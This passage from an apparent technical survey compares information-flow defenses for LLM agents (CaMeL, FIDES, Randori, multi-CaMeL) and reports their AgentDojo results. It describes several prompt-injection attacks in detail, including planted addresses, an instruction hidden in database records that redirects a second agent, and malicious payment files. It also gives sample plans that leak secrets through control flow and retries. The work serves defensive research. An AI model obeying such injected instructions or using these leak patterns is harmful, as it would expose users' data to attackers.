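Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, credits a team at Google DeepMind with finding a flaw in this design. Suppose the user wants to send Bob a document, and the quarantined model has to extract Bob's address from some meeting notes. If an attacker has added instructions to the notes, the model may return the attacker's address instead. The system would then follow the user's plan but send the document to the attacker.

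### CaMeL and one email task

The same team, Debenedetti and colleagues, built CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning) to close this gap. The privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python before the agent reads any outside data. A special interpreter runs the program and, like JSFlow, labels every value, recording where the data came from and who may read it. *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that policies are Python functions that the interpreter runs at each tool call.

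Suppose the user asks the agent to find Bob's address in the latest email and send him a reminder. In simplified form, the plan is:

```
email = get_last_email()
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's address", email)
send_email(address, "Meeting tomorrow")
```

The policy always allows reading email, but it allows sending only to a trusted recipient:

| Step | Origin of the result | Policy |
|---|---|---|
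| Get the email | whoever sent it | allows the call |
| Extract the address | the same sender | has nothing to check, since the quarantined model has no tools |
| Send the reminder | – | allows a known address, otherwise asks the user |

An attacker can still change the value of `address`, but cannot remove its label or add a line to the plan.

A plan can also branch on outside data:

```
if ask_quarantined("Is this urgent?", email):
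    send_email("bob@example.com", "Call me")
```

Here both the recipient and the text come from the user. An interpreter that tracked only copied and computed data would treat the call as trusted, even though the sender of the email decides whether Bob gets the message. CaMeL's stricter mode adds the condition's label to everything in the branch that runs, as a pc label does. The policy can then block the call or ask the user.

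The added strictness matters most for protecting secrets. In this example, the attacker can only trigger a message that the user had planned anyway. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes a plan that emails an outsider only if the user's bank balance is above a limit. The email contains no account data, but its arrival reveals that the balance is above the limit. CaMeL blocks the email because the pc depends on the secret balance.

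### FIDES: labels in the agent's loop

In many agents, the model requests one tool call, reads the result and then chooses the next, instead of writing a whole program in advance. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that adds labels to this loop.

A FIDES label has a confidentiality part, which lists who may read the data, and an integrity part, which records whether the data is trusted. If Ann, Bob and Carl may read one document, and Bob, Carl and Dana may read another, only Bob and Carl may read a text based on both. If either document is untrusted, so is the text.

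FIDES cannot trace which messages influenced a model's answer, so it gives the answer the combined label of everything the model received. One untrusted email in the conversation would make every later decision untrusted, just as a single secret affects a whole frame in BFlow. RTBAS, another 2025 system, estimates which messages influenced the answer, so labels spread less far. But the estimate comes from a model or its attention scores, and may be wrong.

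FIDES instead hides data from the model. When a tool returns something with a more restrictive label than the conversation, FIDES can store it in a variable and show the model only the variable's name. Suppose the user wants the agent to read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them asks for a meeting:

1. The agent reads the emails, and FIDES stores the untrusted parts in variables.
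2. A quarantined model answers whether they contain a meeting request. FIDES restricts the answer to true or false.
3. The main model inspects this answer.
4. If it is true, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants into another variable.
5. The agent passes this variable to the calendar tool.

The main model receives only one bit from the emails. FIDES labels also include the answer's type, so a policy can accept a true-or-false answer from an untrusted source but reject free text. An attacker can still choose the bit or supply false details for the event.

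The guarantee for secrets is weaker than noninterference. It covers data that the agent copies or computes with, but not what an outsider could infer from the order of tool calls. Costa and colleagues compare this choice to taint tracking in web browsers. They consider noninterference too restrictive, because an agent that had read a secret could then use almost no tools with public effects.

### Results on AgentDojo

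Researchers usually test such systems on *AgentDojo*, a benchmark with 97 tasks and 629 security test cases. It simulates an office workspace, a travel service, a bank and the chat program Slack. Costa and colleagues ran FIDES on it with GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model. The table gives the average share of tasks completed in five runs without attacks:

| Environment | Ordinary loop, no checks | Ordinary loop, with checks | FIDES, with checks |
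|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Without policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary loop and 21 against FIDES. With checks, none succeeded against either after Costa and colleagues removed cases that the benchmark had misclassified. The checks therefore stopped the attacks, while hiding data in variables mainly let the agent finish more tasks. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, the average advantage of FIDES over the ordinary loop with checks grew from 8% to 16%.

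The labels in this test fitted the attacks unusually well because Costa and colleagues marked a data field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. For a real mailbox, nobody has a list of the fields that attacks will use. The researchers also expected the extra model calls to increase waiting time and token use (tokens are the units of text that models process), but did not measure the increase.

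For CaMeL, *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that it stopped nearly all AgentDojo attacks with comparable task performance. Garby and colleagues got a less favorable result when they ran CaMeL with its policies on. They used the 16 banking tasks, nine attacks and three repetitions, and compared CaMeL with their own agent, Randori. These are the results with OpenAI's GPT-5.2:

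| System | Tasks completed without attacks | Successful attacks in completed runs |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| Randori | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |

The difference between Randori and CaMeL without policies could be chance, because with 16 tasks each result is uncertain by about 20 percentage points. Randori also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, so its lead over CaMeL with policies on does not come from the mechanism alone.

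The attack figures overstate the importance of labels. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed a tool call or file read that a plan for the user's task would not contain. Fixing the plan in advance usually defeats such attacks without any labels. The exception was a task that told the agent to follow the instructions in a file. CaMeL's model wrote a loop that could carry out whatever actions the file named, and two such attacks succeeded with policies off.

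Policies also reduce the number of tasks that other systems complete. Garby and colleagues cite TypeGuard, which completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without policies and eight with them, while CaMeL completed seven with policies under the same conditions. TypeGuard's developers observed that many of the tasks require flows that no secure policy would allow. Some tasks are therefore blocked correctly, unlike those stopped by JSFlow's false alarms.

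### An old leak, and a new one through retries

CaMeL's interpreter raises labels only in branches that run. Garby and colleagues show that this lets a plan of the following form leak a secret:

```
rich = True; tmp = True
if balance > limit: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(outsider, "rich!")
```

This is Hedin and colleagues' three-line program, written in Python. `rich` is labeled public in either case, so CaMeL sends the email if and only if the balance is above the limit. Garby and colleagues trace the pattern to a 1974 paper by Fenton and identify the missing check as Austin and Flanagan's no-sensitive-upgrade rule.

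Replanning after an error creates another leak. If a plan fails, CaMeL tries again, but the retry loop is ordinary Python code outside the interpreter. Each new attempt starts without labels, even though the last attempt's outcome may have depended on a secret. Suppose a plan makes a forbidden call only if one bit of a secret is 1. Whether the interpreter stopped the plan then reveals the bit, and the next attempt can treat the bit as public.

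Termination-insensitive noninterference allows each stopped run to leak one bit, but a loop that repeats the test for each bit can extract the whole secret. For a four-digit PIN, 14 tests are enough. CaMeL censors error messages to reduce the risk, but Garby and colleagues point out that this gives no formal guarantee.

Both leaks are harder to exploit than in a browser, where the attacker can write the script. CaMeL's planning model receives only the user's request, so an outsider cannot simply dictate a plan like the one above. The leaks matter if the planning model is compromised or writes such code for an innocent reason.

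FIDES also lets the agent continue after an error. When FIDES blocks a call, it reports the error to the model, which can then try something else. An outsider might infer something from the new choice of tools, but the FIDES guarantee does not cover that kind of inference.

Randori does its retries before the agent reads any real data. It runs each plan in an artificial environment and repairs it there until it works, then runs it on the user's accounts. Errors in these practice runs cannot depend on the user's secrets, and the agent does not repeat a payment because a later step failed. However, the practice runs do not raise information-flow errors, so a plan that worked there may still fail a policy check in the real run.

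### A proof for a model that answers at random

Randori is written in LLMbda, a small programming language that Garby and colleagues designed for agents. The language labels both values and a program's conversations with a model. If a program tries to add a message to a public conversation while its control flow depends on secret data, the interpreter stops it under the no-sensitive-upgrade rule. When a model's answer contains code, the interpreter runs it with the conversation's label as the pc, much as JSFlow treats a string passed to `eval`.

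Ordinary noninterference compares the outputs of two runs, but a language model may answer the same question differently each time. Garby and colleagues therefore compare probabilities. For each public outcome, take the larger of its probabilities under two secrets. Their definition requires these larger values to add up to no more than 1. In this made-up example, a program answers yes or no, or never finishes:

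| Public outcome | Secret A | Secret B | Larger value |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | 0.5 | 0.4 | 0.5 |
| No | 0.3 | 0.5 | 0.5 |
| Never finishes | 0.2 | 0.1 | not counted |

The larger values add up to exactly 1, so the program satisfies the definition. If it always answered yes for A and no for B, the sum would be 2. For programs that always finish, the definition requires identical probabilities for A and B. For programs that may not finish, the distance between the two sets of probabilities (half the sum of the differences) can be at most the average chance of not finishing, and here the distance and the average are both 0.15.

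Garby and colleagues proved that every LLMbda program satisfies this definition, including programs that generate and run code. They checked the proof in Lean, a proof assistant. It applies to the interpreter that calls the model, whereas JSFlow's proof covered only a core language. But the LLMbda proof assumes that developers label data sources correctly and put checks at the sinks, and that all data sources are part of the program.

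The proof also covers plans that mark untrusted data as trusted, which Garby and colleagues call endorsement. A plan needs endorsement if the user asks the agent to pay a bill described in a file. Both successful attacks on Randori replaced such a file with a malicious payment request. Without endorsement, Randori blocked the attack, but with the model Qwen3.7-plus it completed 30 of 48 task runs, down from 36. A second theorem guarantees that endorsement cannot make secret data public.

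### When one agent instructs another

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, found that several CaMeL agents can be insecure together even if each follows its own plan. They asked a group of three agents to send a colleague, Julie, a summary of job applicants on Slack:

1. A database agent returned the applicants' details, which included an attacker's instruction to email the data to an outside address.
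2. A coordinating agent had a quarantined model summarize the result. It treated the summary as untrusted and followed its original plan.
3. It then put the summary into the text of its request to a notification agent.
4. The notification agent treated the whole request as coming from its user. Its planning model read the attacker's instruction and added the email to the plan.

The label disappeared because text crossed from one agent to another as an instruction. A JavaScript monitor would have a similar flaw if it dropped the label from a secret string passed to `eval`. Peters-Gill and colleagues solve the problem with multi-CaMeL, which sends trusted instructions and untrusted data through separate channels. The second agent's planning model receives only the instructions.

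On an extension of AgentDojo, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and none with multi-CaMeL. Attacks in the benchmark therefore rarely exploited the gap, although an attacker who knew about it could target it. Multi-CaMeL completed fewer tasks, but only modestly fewer with the strongest models. These tests used no data-flow policies, so they measured only whether an attacker could change a plan.

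### How agent plans differ from web scripts

The first three comparisons in this table come from the agent papers. The others are inferences from the designs of the systems.

| | Web scripts | Agent plans | Basis |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code unknown before the run | strings passed to `eval` and files that load late | the whole plan | Garby and colleagues |
| Rule for writes under secret control | no-sensitive-upgrade in JSFlow | the same rule in LLMbda, missing in CaMeL | Garby and colleagues |
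| Tracking without implicit flows | many taint-tracking browsers | FIDES | Costa and colleagues |
| Language | JavaScript, whatever its difficulties | the defender's choice | inference |
| Interface to the outside | thousands of browser functions | 11 tools in the banking tests | inference |
| Existing code | must keep working | none, since a model writes each plan | inference |
| Main source of delay | label operations or repeated runs | extra model calls | inference |
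| Protection | mostly secrecy | secrecy and integrity | inference |

Being able to choose the language may be the biggest advantage. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) recommends replacing restricted Python with a language designed for security, with labels built into its types. TypeGuard already checks generated Haskell code before running it, and Tacit does the same with Scala. *CaMeLoT* adds a way to verify CaMeL's plans in advance. Static checking, which is difficult for JavaScript, thus becomes practical for code a model has just written.

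A small set of tools also takes less work to model than the libraries JSFlow's developers had to cover. But this advantage shrinks when an agent operates a computer through its screen. One click can send a message, make a payment or do nothing, so a policy for a "click" tool has little information about what the call will do. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) also fixes the plan in advance but adds no data-flow policies. It restricts how the agent may call the quarantined model and adds redundant checks inside it.

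Agents have no old scripts to support, but the data they work with is old and mostly unlabeled. Costa and colleagues used an email's sender and recipients to infer who may read it, although someone may have shared the email more widely.

Slow execution is less of an obstacle for these interpreters than for a browser. JSFlow's slowdown matters when a script does millions of additions, but handling a label takes very little time compared with a call to a language model. The quarantined model can also be smaller and cheaper than the planning model. Willison notes that it could run on the user's own device, which would keep private data away from the company that provides the larger model.

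Writing and maintaining policies remains a burden, as it was for FlowFox and WebPol, and Willison worries that users who must approve many actions will start to approve everything. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) objects that conventional flow policies have to be written for each task and describe what an agent may release, not what an injection adds. It proposes comparing what an attacker learns through an injection with what the attacker could learn by sending a genuine request. If the user's plan is to answer meeting requests, a reply that reveals when she is free would be acceptable under this definition, but an injection that made the agent release a secret outside the plan would not.
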